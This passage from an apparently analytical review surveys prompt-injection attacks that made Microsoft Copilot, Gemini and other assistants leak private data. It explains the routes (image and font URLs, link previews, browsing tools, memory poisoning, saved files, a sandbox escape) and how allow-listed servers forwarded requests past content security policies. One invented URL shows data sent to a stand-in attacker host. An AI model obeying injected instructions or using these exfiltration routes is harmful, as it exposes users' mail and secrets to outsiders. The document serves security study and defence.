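The first change would have stopped the attack as he built it, but an attacker could have switched to visible characters, at a higher risk of the victim noticing. Either of the other two changes would have been more effective. Without automatic search, the attacker could not have chosen what to take from the mailbox, and without links, Copilot could not have sent the result out by this route.

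Only the change to links was visible from outside. Rehberger saw that Copilot no longer rendered them. Bargury (2024), who was attacking the product separately, lists "No URLs or images" among the barriers an attacker faced in *Living off Microsoft Copilot*, a set of slides from the same August. The restriction had at least one gap, because in the demonstration that Willison describes, the victim could still click on a link to a page that Copilot had found through a web search.

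Rehberger asked Microsoft to explain the fix so that other companies could learn from it, but got no answer. Microsoft came closest to explaining it in a general account from 2025. There, the company says it blocked the image leak that Rehberger had reported and took similar steps against other methods, including "the generation of certain untrusted links". This fits the 2024 case well, but Microsoft does not name it.

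By early 2025 Copilot was removing links to outside sites from its answers before users could click them. Ravia's team discovered this while building EchoLeak, and found that the filter recognised the usual Markdown syntax for links but missed a less common one. It may be the same filter that stopped Rehberger's attack in 2024, or a later replacement. Either way, Microsoft had adopted something close to his third recommendation, but it worked only if the filter recognised every form of link.

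There is less evidence of the other two. It is unknown whether Microsoft filtered tag characters in Copilot in 2024. Microsoft (2026) now advises organisations to strip these characters from email before an AI assistant reads it. When Rehberger introduced the ASCII Smuggler in January 2024, he had already called for applications to filter the response as well as the prompt. In the Copilot attack, the response contained the stolen text.

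Two years after Rehberger's first report, a stranger's text could still make Copilot search a user's email automatically. The attack that Microsoft fixed in March 2026 depended on such a search. Rehberger shared a Word document containing hostile instructions, and when the user typed a greeting to Copilot, it searched for an email with a particular subject.

This is probably the hardest of the three recommendations to follow. People buy Copilot to search their mail and files without telling it exactly where to look, and if it asked for confirmation before every search, they would soon click through without reading. It would be better to allow searches that serve Ana's question and block those requested by a stranger's email, but Copilot would have to distinguish Ana's instructions from the email's, and prompt injection is possible because it can't do this reliably. Removing links is much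 easier. Ana loses some convenience, but a program can remove them without judging anyone's intentions.

Rehberger noted in August that prompt injection itself still worked.

### What one demonstration can establish

The demonstration showed that every step of the attack could work in sequence on a product companies were already using. Microsoft's response supports this. It opened a case within three days of receiving the full attack, asked for several weeks to prepare a fix, and did not dispute the write-up when it reviewed a draft.

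Rehberger calls the attack chain reliable but doesn't report how many times he tried it, so its success rate is unclear. In *Who Am I?* he writes that language models mostly follow instructions "but not always", and that this is a problem for attackers too. His test with three recipients worked as planned for all three, but a method that works only 37% of the time would produce the same result in about one such test in twenty.

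A full attack requires five steps to succeed. The victim has to use Copilot on the hostile message, Copilot has to follow the instructions, find the right email and encode it correctly, and the victim has to click. If each step worked 80% of the time, independently of the others, the attack would work about 33% of the time. These figures are only an illustration, since nobody measured the real ones. The last step is probably the least certain, because Rehberger tested the software and not whether an unsuspecting employee would click.

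This case also differs from EchoLeak in its first step. According to Ravia, earlier attacks either required the user to point the chatbot at the malicious material or severely limited what an attacker could take. In Rehberger's published sequence, the user asks Copilot about the malicious document. He says ordinary retrieval could also deliver the instructions, but his sequence doesn't rely on it.

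Rehberger reports no real victims. *Microsoft Copilot Vulnerability Exposed Sensitive Data* (2024), an entry in the OECD's AI incidents monitor, classes the case as a "realized" attack, but this is true only in the sense that a researcher carried it out. The absence of known victims is weak evidence that there were none, because a click on one of these links would have looked like any other website visit and the victim would have had little reason to report it. Microsoft was better placed to search for traces, and for EchoLeak it stated that no customers had been affected. Rehberger's account contains no such statement about the 2024 flaw.

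The case also doesn't show that other assistants were open to the same attack. The attack requires a model that can write tag characters accurately, access to private data, a search that a stranger's text can start, and an interface that leaves the characters in the link. Products differed on each of these, and some changed from month to month. The link was the most widely shared weakness. *Trust No AI* reports that Amazon's assistant for companies, Q for Business, also had a flaw that let data out, and that Amazon responded by no longer rendering links. Rehberger's summary of that case doesn't mention hidden characters.

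## Case reports of images, styles and fonts that leak data

Rehberger's 2024 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot worked only if the victim clicked a link. Images, background pictures and fonts need no click, because the browser requests them from a web address to display an answer.

Researchers have leaked data from Microsoft's chatbots this way since 2023. Microsoft added a CSP after the first report and several filters later, so subsequent attacks had to bypass these defenses.

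### Bing Chat in 2023

The first report concerned Bing Chat, which could read whatever web page the user had open. Embrace The Red describes how a stranger could use a comment or advertisement on that page to instruct the chatbot to write a Markdown image. The image's address contained a 200-character summary of the page and the conversation, followed by any passwords on the page. In Rehberger's demonstration, a secret from further down the page reached his server.

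The image appeared only after two more exchanges. Rehberger added this delay to show that the injected text still controlled Bing Chat after the conversation had moved on. The delay would also make it harder for a victim to guess the cause.

He had the chatbot write the data in base64, which turns every three bytes into four ordinary characters. A 200-character English summary becomes 268 characters, compared with 2,400 in percent-encoded tag characters. The image loaded without a click, so he had no reason to hide the text.

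Rehberger reported the flaw on 8 April 2023, and Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed the problem. The fix apparently included the new CSP, which allowed images from only four servers, all belonging to Bing. His earlier attacks no longer worked, but Bing Chat also seemed to have blocklisted his test site, which makes his failed retests a little harder to interpret.

ChatGPT had the same weakness. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) describes an attack by Roman Samoilenko that used a one-pixel image. Samoilenko's web page added instructions to any text a visitor copied from it, in the hope that the visitor would paste the text into ChatGPT without looking. OpenAI started to address the leak in December 2023. In a 2026 retrospective, Embrace The Red credits Microsoft as the first vendor to fix the problem, ahead of Anthropic, Google, GitHub and OpenAI.

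### EchoLeak

By 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot had an injection detector, a filter for external links and a content security policy (CSP). EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) bypassed all three. The attacker also had Copilot omit the malicious email from the answer's references, where a message from a stranger might have looked odd.

The link filter missed reference-style Markdown links, in which a short label follows the link text and the address appears elsewhere in the answer beside the same label, like a footnote. The software that displayed the answer rendered these as working links. The filter also missed reference-style images.

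The remaining obstacle was the CSP, which blocked images from the attacker's server. Ravia's published list of allowed servers has 29 different entries, including 11 wildcards that allow every server under a name such as `bing.com` or `sharepoint.com`. Bing Chat had needed only four entries, but 365 Copilot works with SharePoint, Teams and many other services, each of which may have its own images to display.

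Ravia's team looked for an allowed server that would pass a request on to an outside one. Here is the general idea, with invented names:

`https://allowed.example/preview?url=https://stranger.example/blue-kettle`

Ana's browser finds the first server name on the CSP's list and sends the request. The allowed server then fetches the second address, perhaps to prepare a preview of the page, and the code name appears in the stranger's log. The CSP has no effect on the second request because the server sends it, not Ana's browser. Security researchers call this weakness server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an outsider can make a trusted server send a request the outsider has chosen.

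The team first found such a function in SharePoint. Any customer, including an attacker, can have a site under `sharepoint.com`, and these sites could fetch outside content to embed it. But this worked only if the victim had signed in to SharePoint and accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, which someone who had never heard of the site would be unlikely to do. The team then found a Teams address that fetched outside content without an invitation. Reddy and Gujral identify it as part of a preview service.

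According to Ravia, the attack could take anything in the context window, including earlier messages in the chat, retrieved emails and files, and the names of the user and the company.

INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), an entry in the vulnerability database of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, gives EchoLeak a critical CVSS score of 9.3. According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft made initial repairs by April 2025 and completed the fix on its own servers in May. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports that customers did not need to do anything. Ravia knew of no administrator setting that would have prevented the attack before the fix.

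Microsoft's changes are less clear. Reddy and Gujral say that Copilot now strips reference links and embedded images from outside content before the model reads it. That would remove an address the attacker supplied in one of those forms, but it would not stop the model from writing an image of its own. They worked only from public accounts and don't explain whether Microsoft also took Teams off the list or stopped the preview service from fetching outside addresses.

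Willison called EchoLeak an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. This is a fair description of the leak itself, since the technique of putting private data in an image address was two years old by then. Delivering the attack by unsolicited email and routing the data through an allowed server were newer.

In June 2025, another researcher found a similar way around the CSP in GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes the attack, which used GitHub's own infrastructure and could take passwords and source code from private projects. GitHub responded by turning off all images in Copilot Chat, so attackers no longer had a list of allowed image servers to study.

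### SearchLeak

Microsoft continued to display images and to rely on a list of allowed domains. Its July 2025 account of its defences distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail. Microsoft classes its fix for the Markdown image leak as deterministic, and says it looks for variants of the same flaw after any report. A year later, a variant of EchoLeak's indirect route worked through Bing.

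Varonis, a data security firm, published *SearchLeak* on 15 June 2026. The report describes a three-part attack chain against Copilot Enterprise Search, a version of Copilot that searches a company's emails, meetings and files.

The attack began with a crafted link to the genuine Microsoft site. Copilot treated the search query in the link's address as a prompt, so a single click would have made it search Ana's mailbox for information the stranger wanted. A safeguard that examined only emails and documents would not have checked the instructions in the link.

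Copilot then wrote an image tag, the HTML equivalent of a Markdown image. To guard against this, Microsoft wrapped Copilot's output in a code block so that the browser would show the tag as text instead of loading the image. But Copilot displays its answers piece by piece as it generates them, and the code block was added only at the end. Until then, the browser treated the unfinished answer as ordinary HTML and requested the image.

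Varonis calls this a race condition, a flaw in which the result depends on which of two events happens first. If, for example, an answer takes five seconds to generate and the image tag is complete after two, the browser has three seconds to send a request before the wrapping is applied. Sending one normally takes a small fraction of a second. The wrapping then worked as intended and turned the tag into harmless text on the screen.

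Finally, the request had to get past the CSP, which allowed every server under `bing.com`. Bing's search-by-image feature lets a user supply the address of a picture, which Bing's servers then fetch for analysis. The request gave this feature an address on the attacker's server that contained the stolen text. When Bing fetched that address, it sent the text to the attacker.

Microsoft had allowed `www.bing.com` in Bing Chat's policy in 2023, and Ravia's 2025 list for 365 Copilot included a wildcard covering all of Bing. Anyone who read that list after EchoLeak could have asked which Bing services fetch URLs that users supply. Varonis now recommends this check for any server on a CSP's list.

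The attack in Varonis's published example steals the subject line of an email, where companies often put sign-in codes. Varonis also lists salary information, acquisition plans and meeting notes among the data at risk. That list follows from what Copilot could search on the user's behalf, but the published steps don't demonstrate the theft of each item.

The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* points out that filters based on a site's reputation would have allowed this link. A company monitoring its own network would also have seen little, because Ana's computer contacted only Microsoft and Bing.

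Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), its 4 June record for CVE-2026-42824, rates the flaw critical, although the CVSS score is only 6.5, and lists it as fully mitigated and not exploited. The record doesn't specify which of the three parts Microsoft repaired. Varonis considers every part necessary, so repairing one would have been enough to break the chain, but would have left the other two available for use in a new combination.

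### Styles and fonts in the HTML preview

Eight months before SearchLeak became public, Rehberger reported the font leak in 365 Copilot. This leak did not need an allowed server to forward the data. He found it while checking which tools Copilot had. Copilot refused to list them in its answer but wrote their names into a document when he asked for one. While trying out a tool whose name suggested a document editor, he discovered an unrelated feature that let Copilot write a small web page and display a working preview in the chat.

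A web page can request many kinds of file, so the page preview was an obvious place to look for leaks. As precautions, Microsoft removed image tags from the previewed page and showed users the page's code first, so they had to switch to the preview themselves.

Rehberger asked Copilot to write a page using as many methods as it could think of for loading an outside file. One method that worked was naming a background picture in the page's style sheet, the set of rules for its colours, sizes and positions. The filter had removed image tags but not these rules, so the browser tried to fetch the picture.

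The CSP still allowed that picture to load only from a list of approved sources. Rehberger thought the list was long enough to offer ways around the restriction. He also noticed that the different web pages that include Copilot, such as its own chat site, SharePoint and Excel Online, each sent their own list. Some entries were for test and preview versions of Microsoft's services, and some seemed to contain employees' user names. Others were under `azureedge.net`, a hosting domain that Microsoft's customers had also used for their own servers.

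He considered working out which product had which gap, but this turned out to be unnecessary. A CSP has a separate list for each kind of file, as in this invented policy:

`default-src 'self'; img-src pictures.example; font-src *`

The first part sets the default, which allows files only from the page's own server. The other parts override it, allowing images from `pictures.example` and fonts from anywhere. Someone who checked only the image rule would think this page was well protected.

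365 Copilot had a similar imbalance. Its rule for fonts was more permissive than its rule for images and let the browser contact Rehberger's own server. A style sheet can name a font file by its address, so he had Copilot put the stolen text in that address. The attack also required a switch to the preview, which Copilot made itself when the injected text included an instruction to do so. The method worked in the desktop version of Word, Word Online and Excel.

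Microsoft had already used a stricter CSP in the Copilot built into the Edge browser, which Kokatsu (2024) describes in *Piloting Edge Copilot*. The policy had specific lists of allowed sources for images, styles, media and a few other things, and everything else had to come from the page's own server. Fonts had no list of their own, so a font request to an outside server should have failed. Edge's Copilot also enforced a minimum CSP. A similar minimum that covered fonts would have protected 365 Copilot no matter which product displayed it.

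Rehberger reported the problem on 16 October 2025, and Microsoft opened a case two days later. Microsoft reproduced the attack on 12 November, paid him a reward in December, began releasing the fix in late February and finished on 5 March 2026. The fix took 140 days from his report, about twice as long as the Bing Chat fix, perhaps because so many products contained Copilot. MITRE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), the public record for CVE-2026-24299, was published on 19 March and rates the severity as medium, with a score of 5.3.

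Rehberger says the case shows that the CSP was "not a reliable security boundary in Copilot". He thinks companies that sell assistants for other people's websites should state who is responsible for preventing leaks. If an assistant's safety depends on the surrounding page's CSP, a customer who embeds it in a page with a weak policy, or none, unknowingly removes that protection.

### A leak stored in Copilot's memory

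In November 2025 Rehberger sent Microsoft a version of the font attack that continued after the victim had closed the hostile document. Earlier that year, Microsoft had given 365 Copilot a long-term memory, on by default, which stores facts and preferences for use in later conversations.

The hostile document was a biography of Albert Einstein with instructions in the middle. When the user asked for a summary, Copilot gave a normal one and ended by asking whether it had been helpful. Whether the user answered yes or no, Copilot then saved a new memory that the user liked to see passwords and codes in an HTML preview with a particular font. Rehberger calls this delayed tool invocation, because the document sets up an action that the user's next message triggers.

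From then on, whenever the victim typed a password or code into any conversation, Copilot built the preview and the browser requested the font from an address containing the secret. The attack no longer required the victim to open a hostile document or receive a hostile email. The untrusted content, one part of the lethal trifecta, was now in Copilot's own records, and Copilot would treat it as the user's preference in later conversations.

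The attack left signs that a user could see. Copilot displayed "Memory updated" in small type when it saved the instruction, a preview appeared each time it leaked something, and the memory stayed in the user's settings until someone deleted it. But an administrator would have had trouble finding out later when the memory appeared because, according to Microsoft's documentation as Rehberger read it in April 2026, changes to memory created no entries in the audit log.

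Microsoft reported this version fixed on 6 December 2025, three months before it fixed the font request. During those months, an attacker could still use the font request to send data out of a single conversation. Rehberger suspects that Microsoft fixed the memory problem by training the model further and filtering incoming text better. If so, the fix made hostile memories less likely but still possible.

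### How the controls failed

The table sets out what each attack used and what was supposed to stop it.

| Case | Feature that carried the data | Control in place | Why it failed | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat, 2023 | Markdown image | No effective limit on image addresses | The browser loaded images from any server | CSP allowing images from four Bing servers, June 2023 |
| EchoLeak, 2025 | Markdown image in reference form | Removal of outside links and images; CSP | The filter missed the reference form, and an allowed Teams address fetched outside pages | Change on Microsoft's servers, May 2025 |
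| CamoLeak, 2025 | Image in GitHub Copilot Chat | CSP | GitHub's own infrastructure provided a way around it | GitHub turned off images in the chat |
| HTML preview, 2025–26 | Style-sheet background | Removal of image tags; CSP for images | The filter ignored style rules, and the CSP was long and varied between products | Completed 5 March 2026 |
| HTML preview, 2025–26 | Font | Code view by default; CSP for fonts | Copilot opened the preview on request, and the CSP allowed an outside server | Completed 5 March 2026 |
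| Copilot memory, 2025 | Font, in later conversations | User's reply needed before the memory was saved in the demonstration | Any reply to a routine question was enough | Reported fixed 6 December 2025 |
| SearchLeak, 2026 | HTML image tag | Conversion of HTML to plain text; CSP | The conversion came after the browser's request, and an allowed Bing address fetched outside files | Change on Microsoft's servers by 4 June 2026 |

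The filters that cleaned Copilot's output relied on assumptions about how the browser would treat a piece of text. EchoLeak used a form of Markdown that the display software recognised but the filter missed. In the HTML preview, the filter searched for image tags, but the browser also applied style rules. SearchLeak's filter recognised the tag but ran too late.

Listing the few forms an answer needs, such as headings, bold type and tables, and discarding the rest is easier than listing every forbidden form, because HTML and Markdown have many ways of doing the same thing. Reddy and Gujral recommend something close to this, but their list of safe formatting still includes plain images, which would have to be restricted in some other way. Varonis recommends cleaning each piece of an answer before the browser displays it. This is more work when the answer arrives in fragments, because a tag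 may be split between two of them.

The CSP failures were different because the browser followed the policy correctly every time, but the policy allowed too much. Reddy and Gujral advise companies to allow only their own servers and to avoid wildcards. This would shorten the list of allowed servers considerably, but Microsoft owns both Teams and Bing, so a policy limited to Microsoft's servers could still have included them.

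Reddy and Gujral nevertheless rate a strict CSP as one of the few measures that would have stopped EchoLeak, while Rehberger does not trust the CSP in Copilot at all. The two views are compatible, and the CSP did stop the simplest attacks, including Ravia's first attempt to load an image and Rehberger's old attacks on Bing Chat. They differ on whether a company with dozens of services and many host pages can keep its allowlists strict. Microsoft's record since 2025 favours Rehberger's view, because each of the attacks on 365 Copilot used a different gap.

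Some alternatives don't depend on a list of servers. The simplest is to remove images, as GitHub did. Google and OpenAI check individual addresses before loading them, but Rehberger did not think Copilot did this yet. Microsoft has continued to find and close individual gaps. According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), Ravia's research group, now part of the security company Cato Networks, published three more zero-click attacks on 365 Copilot in December 2026 under the name ReLeak, one of which again used an image address.

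### What successful demonstrations cannot show

Researchers publish the attacks that work, and nobody keeps a public count of the attempts that a filter or CSP defeated, so these reports can't show what share of attacks the controls stop. A few details suggest that the share is considerable. Ravia describes trying the allowed services one by one, with several failed attempts in SharePoint, before finding the Teams address. Someone less patient, or less familiar with Microsoft's products, might have given up and published nothing.

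The reports also don't give success rates. Microsoft reproduced the font attack, which confirms that it worked outside Rehberger's own setup, but not how often. For EchoLeak, Ravia reports that Copilot retrieved the hostile email in response to questions on various topics, but not how many questions failed to retrieve it. Reddy and Gujral's academic study doesn't provide measured rates either. They state in the limitations section that they ran no experiments, so although the study refers at one point to "our tests", its table of which defences would have blocked which steps records their judgement.

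A better model would change these unknown rates. EchoLeak worked on a version of Copilot that ran on GPT-4, according to Ravia, and current models follow injected instructions much less often. But if an injection succeeds, the browser still requests the image or font just as reliably as it did in 2023.

The number of cases does not show that Copilot is less secure than its competitors. Microsoft pays researchers for reports and publishes records of flaws in its online services even when customers have nothing to install. It gives transparency as its only reason for publishing the SearchLeak record. If another company fixed the same flaw without disclosing it, there would be no case to count. Copilot is also an attractive target because so many companies keep their mail and files with Microsoft.

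The dates of the Copilot disclosures don't establish a trend. EchoLeak and SearchLeak were a year apart, although The Next Web counts them and an earlier attack by Varonis on the consumer version of Copilot as three disclosures in six months, each bypassing protections that the previous fix was supposed to provide. More reports might mean that Copilot's defences were getting worse, or that it was gaining features such as the HTML preview and more people were examining it.

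The demonstrations took only small amounts of data: a subject line, a password or the text of one email, each of which had to fit into a web address. An attacker who wanted a whole mailbox would need many requests, either from one answer with many images or from many conversations. The memory attack suggests how an attacker might collect data over many conversations, but Rehberger used it only for secrets that the victim typed. None of the published accounts measures how much an attacker could extract before the user noticed the odd pictures and previews or Microsoft noticed the traffic.

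## Case reports of leaks through links, browsing tools and messages

A CSP can stop Ana's browser from fetching a picture for a chatbot's answer, but it doesn't affect requests from other programs. Assistants now post in messaging apps, open web pages, send mail, save files and run code, and any of these actions can make another computer contact the stranger's server.

### Link previews

When someone posts a link in Slack or Telegram, a preview with the page's title and a picture often appears below it. The messaging service fetches the page to build this preview, whether or not anybody clicks the link.

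Suppose Ana's company has connected an assistant to Slack, and she asks it there about the printing contract. A hostile document makes the assistant end its reply with a link to the stranger's server, with the code name "blue-kettle" in the address. Slack's preview service requests the address soon after the reply appears, which puts the code name in the stranger's log. Moving a chatbot into a messaging app can therefore turn a one-click leak into a zero-click one, even with the same model and hostile document. Blocking images in the assistant's answers wouldn't help, because the address is a plain link.

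Rehberger demonstrated this leak in 2024 with a Slack bot. In 2026 the security firm PromptArmor described the same leak in OpenClaw, an open-source agent that people can run on their own computers and talk to through Telegram. The data at risk depends on what the owner has connected to the agent, which might include mail, files and passwords.

A simple remedy is to turn off link previews. Slack lets developers do this for messages a bot posts, and OpenClaw has a similar setting for Telegram. But whoever connects the assistant to the app has to change the setting, and they may not realize that a preview sends a request to an outside server.

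### Browsing tools

Many assistants can open web pages, for instance to check a train time or summarise an article. The model supplies an address, and a tool fetches the page and returns its text. The vendor can't remove these requests the way GitHub removed images from Copilot Chat, because the tool can't work without them.

In September 2025 the security firm Tenable reported that Google's Gemini could leak data through its browsing tool. Google had already restricted links and images in Gemini's answers, so Tenable's researchers had Gemini open a page on their server, with the victim's saved information and location in the address. They planted the instructions for this in the victim's search history, which Gemini read to personalise its answers. A hostile website could add searches to that history when the victim visited, and the victim then only had to use Gemini. Google has fixed the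 flaw. Anthropic also fixed a leak through Claude's web-fetch tool after a case in July 2026.

Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026) gives a more detailed account of such an attack on Copilot Personal, the consumer version of Microsoft's assistant. As in SearchLeak, the victim clicks a crafted link. The link contains a prompt with instructions for Copilot to open a page on the attacker's server, with information about the user in the page's address.

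Copilot had two safeguards against this. It usually wouldn't open an address without a good reason, but the researchers gave it one by wording the prompt carefully. It could also remove private data from an address before opening it, but this check covered only the first request. In a test with an invented secret phrase, Copilot deleted the phrase the first time and sent it intact the second. An attacker could therefore bypass the check by having Copilot do everything twice.

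Varonis thinks Microsoft probably limited the check to the first request for speed. The flaw resembles the one in SearchLeak, where the filter worked but ran too late. In both cases Microsoft had a control that could detect the leak but did not apply it at every point where data could leave.

### A server that asks the next question

When a browsing tool opens an attacker's page, the page's text goes into the model's context window, where it can act as a new instruction. An attacker can't do this with an image loaded by a browser, because the server can return only a picture, which the model never reads.

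Reprompt used this to keep extracting data. The attacker's server answered each request with a question and a new address for the reply. In the published sequence, Copilot sent the user's name, then the time, the user's location, any other information it had about them, and finally a summary of their last conversation. The attacker could use each answer to choose the next question, for example by asking about a bank after learning that the victim worked there.

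Using several requests also gets around the limit on the length of a web address. An address with room for 2,000 characters of English can carry roughly 300 words, so twenty requests could carry about 6,000.

Varonis researcher Dolev Taler told Ars Technica that the attack on Copilot still worked if the victim clicked the link and closed the tab immediately (*A single click mounted a covert, multistage attack against Copilot*, 2026). The requests therefore probably came from Microsoft's servers rather than the victim's browser. If so, even a perfect CSP on the Copilot page would not have blocked them.

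Varonis slightly overstates the attack when it writes that there was no limit to the amount or type of data an attacker could take. The chain of requests removed the limit on quantity, but Copilot could disclose only what it had access to. Varonis suggests that an attacker could ask for a summary of every file the user had opened that day, but the published sequence takes personal details and chat history, not files. Ars Technica likewise lists the victim's name, location and details of events from the chat history.

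Varonis is right that nobody could tell from the link alone which data the attacker wanted, because the later questions came from the server. But the link had to contain the opening prompt, which told Copilot to contact an unfamiliar server and continue from its reply. A filter that examined prompts in links might have flagged that instruction without seeing the later questions.

Varonis contrasts Reprompt with EchoLeak, which worked only when the user asked Copilot a question. Reprompt instead required the user to click a link. Which is easier to get depends on the victim. An office worker who uses Copilot all day will eventually ask it something, while someone who rarely uses it might still click a link to a Microsoft site.

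Microsoft received the report in August 2025 and fixed the flaw in January 2026, according to The Next Web. Reprompt did not affect Microsoft 365 Copilot, the version for companies. Five months later, however, Varonis used another crafted link in its SearchLeak attack on the company version, despite that version's additional safeguards.

### CoSnitch and Copilot's memory

Varonis' *CoSnitch*, published on 18 August 2026, describes another one-click leak in Copilot Personal. As in Reprompt, Copilot sent the data out when it fetched web pages. TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions* reports that the attack combined malicious links with memory poisoning, in which the attacker plants an entry in the assistant's long-term memory. Microsoft fixed the flaw, CVE-2026-24301, on its own servers.

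After Reprompt, Varonis advised vendors to treat prompts in links as untrusted and to keep safeguards active through every later step. Memory makes that advice harder to follow, because a check on the current link or web page can miss an instruction that Copilot saved earlier, as in Rehberger's memory attack on 365 Copilot.

Varonis writes that CoSnitch takes data from enterprises, which is odd for a flaw in a consumer product. The likely explanation is that employees use their personal Copilot for work. Their company's information would then be in an assistant the company did not administer, and would not be protected by the company's official Copilot being unaffected.

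### Mail to the user's own inbox

An assistant that can send mail can leak data by writing to the attacker. A vendor can guard against this by asking the user to approve messages to outsiders. But in a 2026 case, Copilot Cowork, Microsoft's agent for longer office tasks, leaked data through images in a message it sent only to the user's own inbox.

This leak works like the image leak, except that Ana's mail program requests the image when it displays the message. It would still happen if Cowork's chat window blocked all images.

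Mail programs have long defended against tracking images by not loading pictures from unknown senders until the reader asks for them. This works poorly here because the message comes from Ana's own assistant, which she has every reason to trust. An approval rule based on the recipient has a similar weakness, because a note to Ana about her own work looks harmless and the outsider's address appears only inside the message.

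### ReLeak

Cato AI Labs, the group that disclosed EchoLeak, disclosed the three ReLeak attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot on 3 December 2026. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) describes them as zero-click attacks that use an email to steal data.

All three attacks begin as EchoLeak did, with a hostile email that Copilot retrieves when Ana asks an ordinary work question, even if she never opens the email. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft's injection defences blocked none of them. Copilot could then use anything Ana had permission to see, and the attacks differed only in how the data got out.

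Copilot put the data in an image URL, and Bing passed the request on to the attacker's server. In *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a Russian report on the disclosure, Antipov (2026) notes that the attack resembles SearchLeak, which required a click.

Microsoft listed SearchLeak as fully mitigated on 4 June, but Cato reported its three findings between 29 July and 20 August. Either Microsoft had broken the SearchLeak chain at some other point and left Bing able to forward requests, or Cato found another way to make Bing forward them. In both cases, attackers could still use an allowed server that fetches outside addresses, even after the first repair.

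**A link in a saved file.** Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them in OneDrive or SharePoint, Microsoft's online storage services. In this attack, it saved a file with a link whose address contained private data. Microsoft's servers process saved files in the background, and that processing sent the data out.

Antipov reports that in Cato's tests this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the employee never opened the file. Ana could have read Copilot's answer, found nothing wrong and closed the window before anything left the company. The request didn't involve a browser, so no page's CSP could have blocked it. The file might still help an investigator, since it would contain the address and the stolen text unless somebody deleted it.

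This is like a link preview in that a service fetches an address because it appears in some content. But Slack users can see previews and have some idea that Slack has looked at the page. Few users would expect that just storing a document could make a service contact a server named in it.

Copilot can write and run Python programs, for example to analyse a spreadsheet. It runs them in a sandbox, an isolated environment meant to limit what a program can do. Microsoft states in its documentation that no network traffic can enter or leave the sandbox, but Cato's researchers broke the isolation and sent data directly to an outside server.

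Here the answer on Ana's screen need not contain a link or an image. A program can also send data without putting it in a web address, so this route could presumably carry more data, although neither Antipov nor Faisal reports how much Cato extracted. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, with a CVSS score of 8.6, up from an initial 7.4. Agents that customers build with Agent Builder and Copilot Studio can use the same kind of sandbox, but no one has confirmed that the flaw affected them.

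Microsoft fixed all three on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Cato said it knew of no affected customers. Faisal's subheading attributes that statement to Microsoft. Coming from Microsoft, it would be stronger evidence, because Microsoft can search its own records and Cato can't see most customers' traffic.

### What the victims did and what closed the leaks

| Case | What the victim does | Data within reach | What contacts the attacker's server | What closes the leak |
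|---|---|---|---|---|
| Slack and Telegram previews | Uses the assistant in a messaging app | Whatever the assistant can read | The messaging service | Turning off previews for the assistant's messages |
| Gemini, 2025 | Visits a hostile site and later uses Gemini | Saved information and location | Gemini's browsing tool | Google's fix |
| Reprompt, 2026 | Clicks a link to Copilot | Personal details and chat history | Copilot's page-fetching | Microsoft's fix, January 2026 |
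| CoSnitch, 2026 | Clicks a link | Data in Copilot Personal | Copilot's page-fetching | Microsoft's fix on its servers |
| Copilot Cowork, 2026 | Opens mail from the agent | Whatever the agent can read | The mail program | Not loading outside images in the agent's mail |
| ReLeak, image | Asks Copilot a work question | Anything the user may open | Bing, after a request from the browser | Microsoft's fix, 15 November 2026 |
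| ReLeak, saved file | Asks Copilot a work question | Anything the user may open | Microsoft's file processing | Microsoft's fix, 11 November 2026 |
| ReLeak, code | Asks Copilot a work question | Anything the user may open | A program in the sandbox | Microsoft's fix, 17 September 2026 |

In the two attacks on Copilot Personal, the user's click delivered the instructions. 365 Copilot, the company product, searches its user's mail, so an attacker can send instructions by email and wait for Copilot to find them. This is why the zero-click attacks were on 365 Copilot, even though Microsoft had given it more safeguards. It also has access to more data worth stealing.

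A ban on images in the chat window would have stopped only the Bing route in this table. Another program displayed the image in Cowork's mail, and the other routes used no image. A ban on clickable links would have stopped none of these leaks, since none needed the victim to click a link in the assistant's answer.

The code flaw differs from the other cases because the sandbox was never meant to contact the internet, and Microsoft fixed the flaw by enforcing that restriction again. Browsing tools, link previews and Bing's image service have to fetch outside addresses to work, so their owners must decide which requests to allow.

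That may explain the order of the ReLeak fixes. Microsoft fixed the sandbox 28 to 50 days after Cato's report, depending on when in the reporting period Cato sent it. Fixing the file route took 83 to 105 days, and fixing the Bing route took 87 to 109. Severity may also explain the order, but the CVE records for the other two flaws were still unpublished when Cato disclosed them, so there are no public scores to compare.

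Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells AI security products and benefits if companies agree, but its evidence is fairly strong. The same group attacked the same product with the same kind of email more than a year later, and succeeded by three routes. However, two of the routes depended on Copilot's ability to create files and run code, so Microsoft could have closed every gap that EchoLeak used and still have been vulnerable to both.

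### AI systems that help to find the leaks

EchoLeak took patience and a good knowledge of Microsoft's services, which gave Copilot some protection from less skilled attackers. That protection is probably weakening, because AI agents can now do some of the work. For ReLeak, Cato's researchers directed agents that wrote test cases, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next tests. Such agents can also take over repetitive tasks like trying many allowed services one after another, as Ravia's team did for EchoLeak.

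For CoSnitch, Varonis researchers questioned Copilot about itself. Its answers exposed the weakness, so the researchers did not have to reverse-engineer the product. Varonis calls this "meta-hacking". Rehberger had done something similar when he had Copilot write the names of its tools into a document.

An assistant can describe its own workings incorrectly, so a researcher still has to test what it says. But an attacker who gets a wrong answer only has to try again. Vendors can use the same methods before release, and they can also read the source code and server logs.

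## Controlled experiments on hidden instructions and silent leaks

Case reports show that an attack worked, but hardly any give its success rate. To measure it, researchers build a small test system, plant an invented secret or a hidden instruction, and repeat the same attack dozens or hundreds of times. Several groups did this in 2026. The rates they found depended heavily on the setup. The same model leaked in 88% of runs in one experiment and 10% in another.

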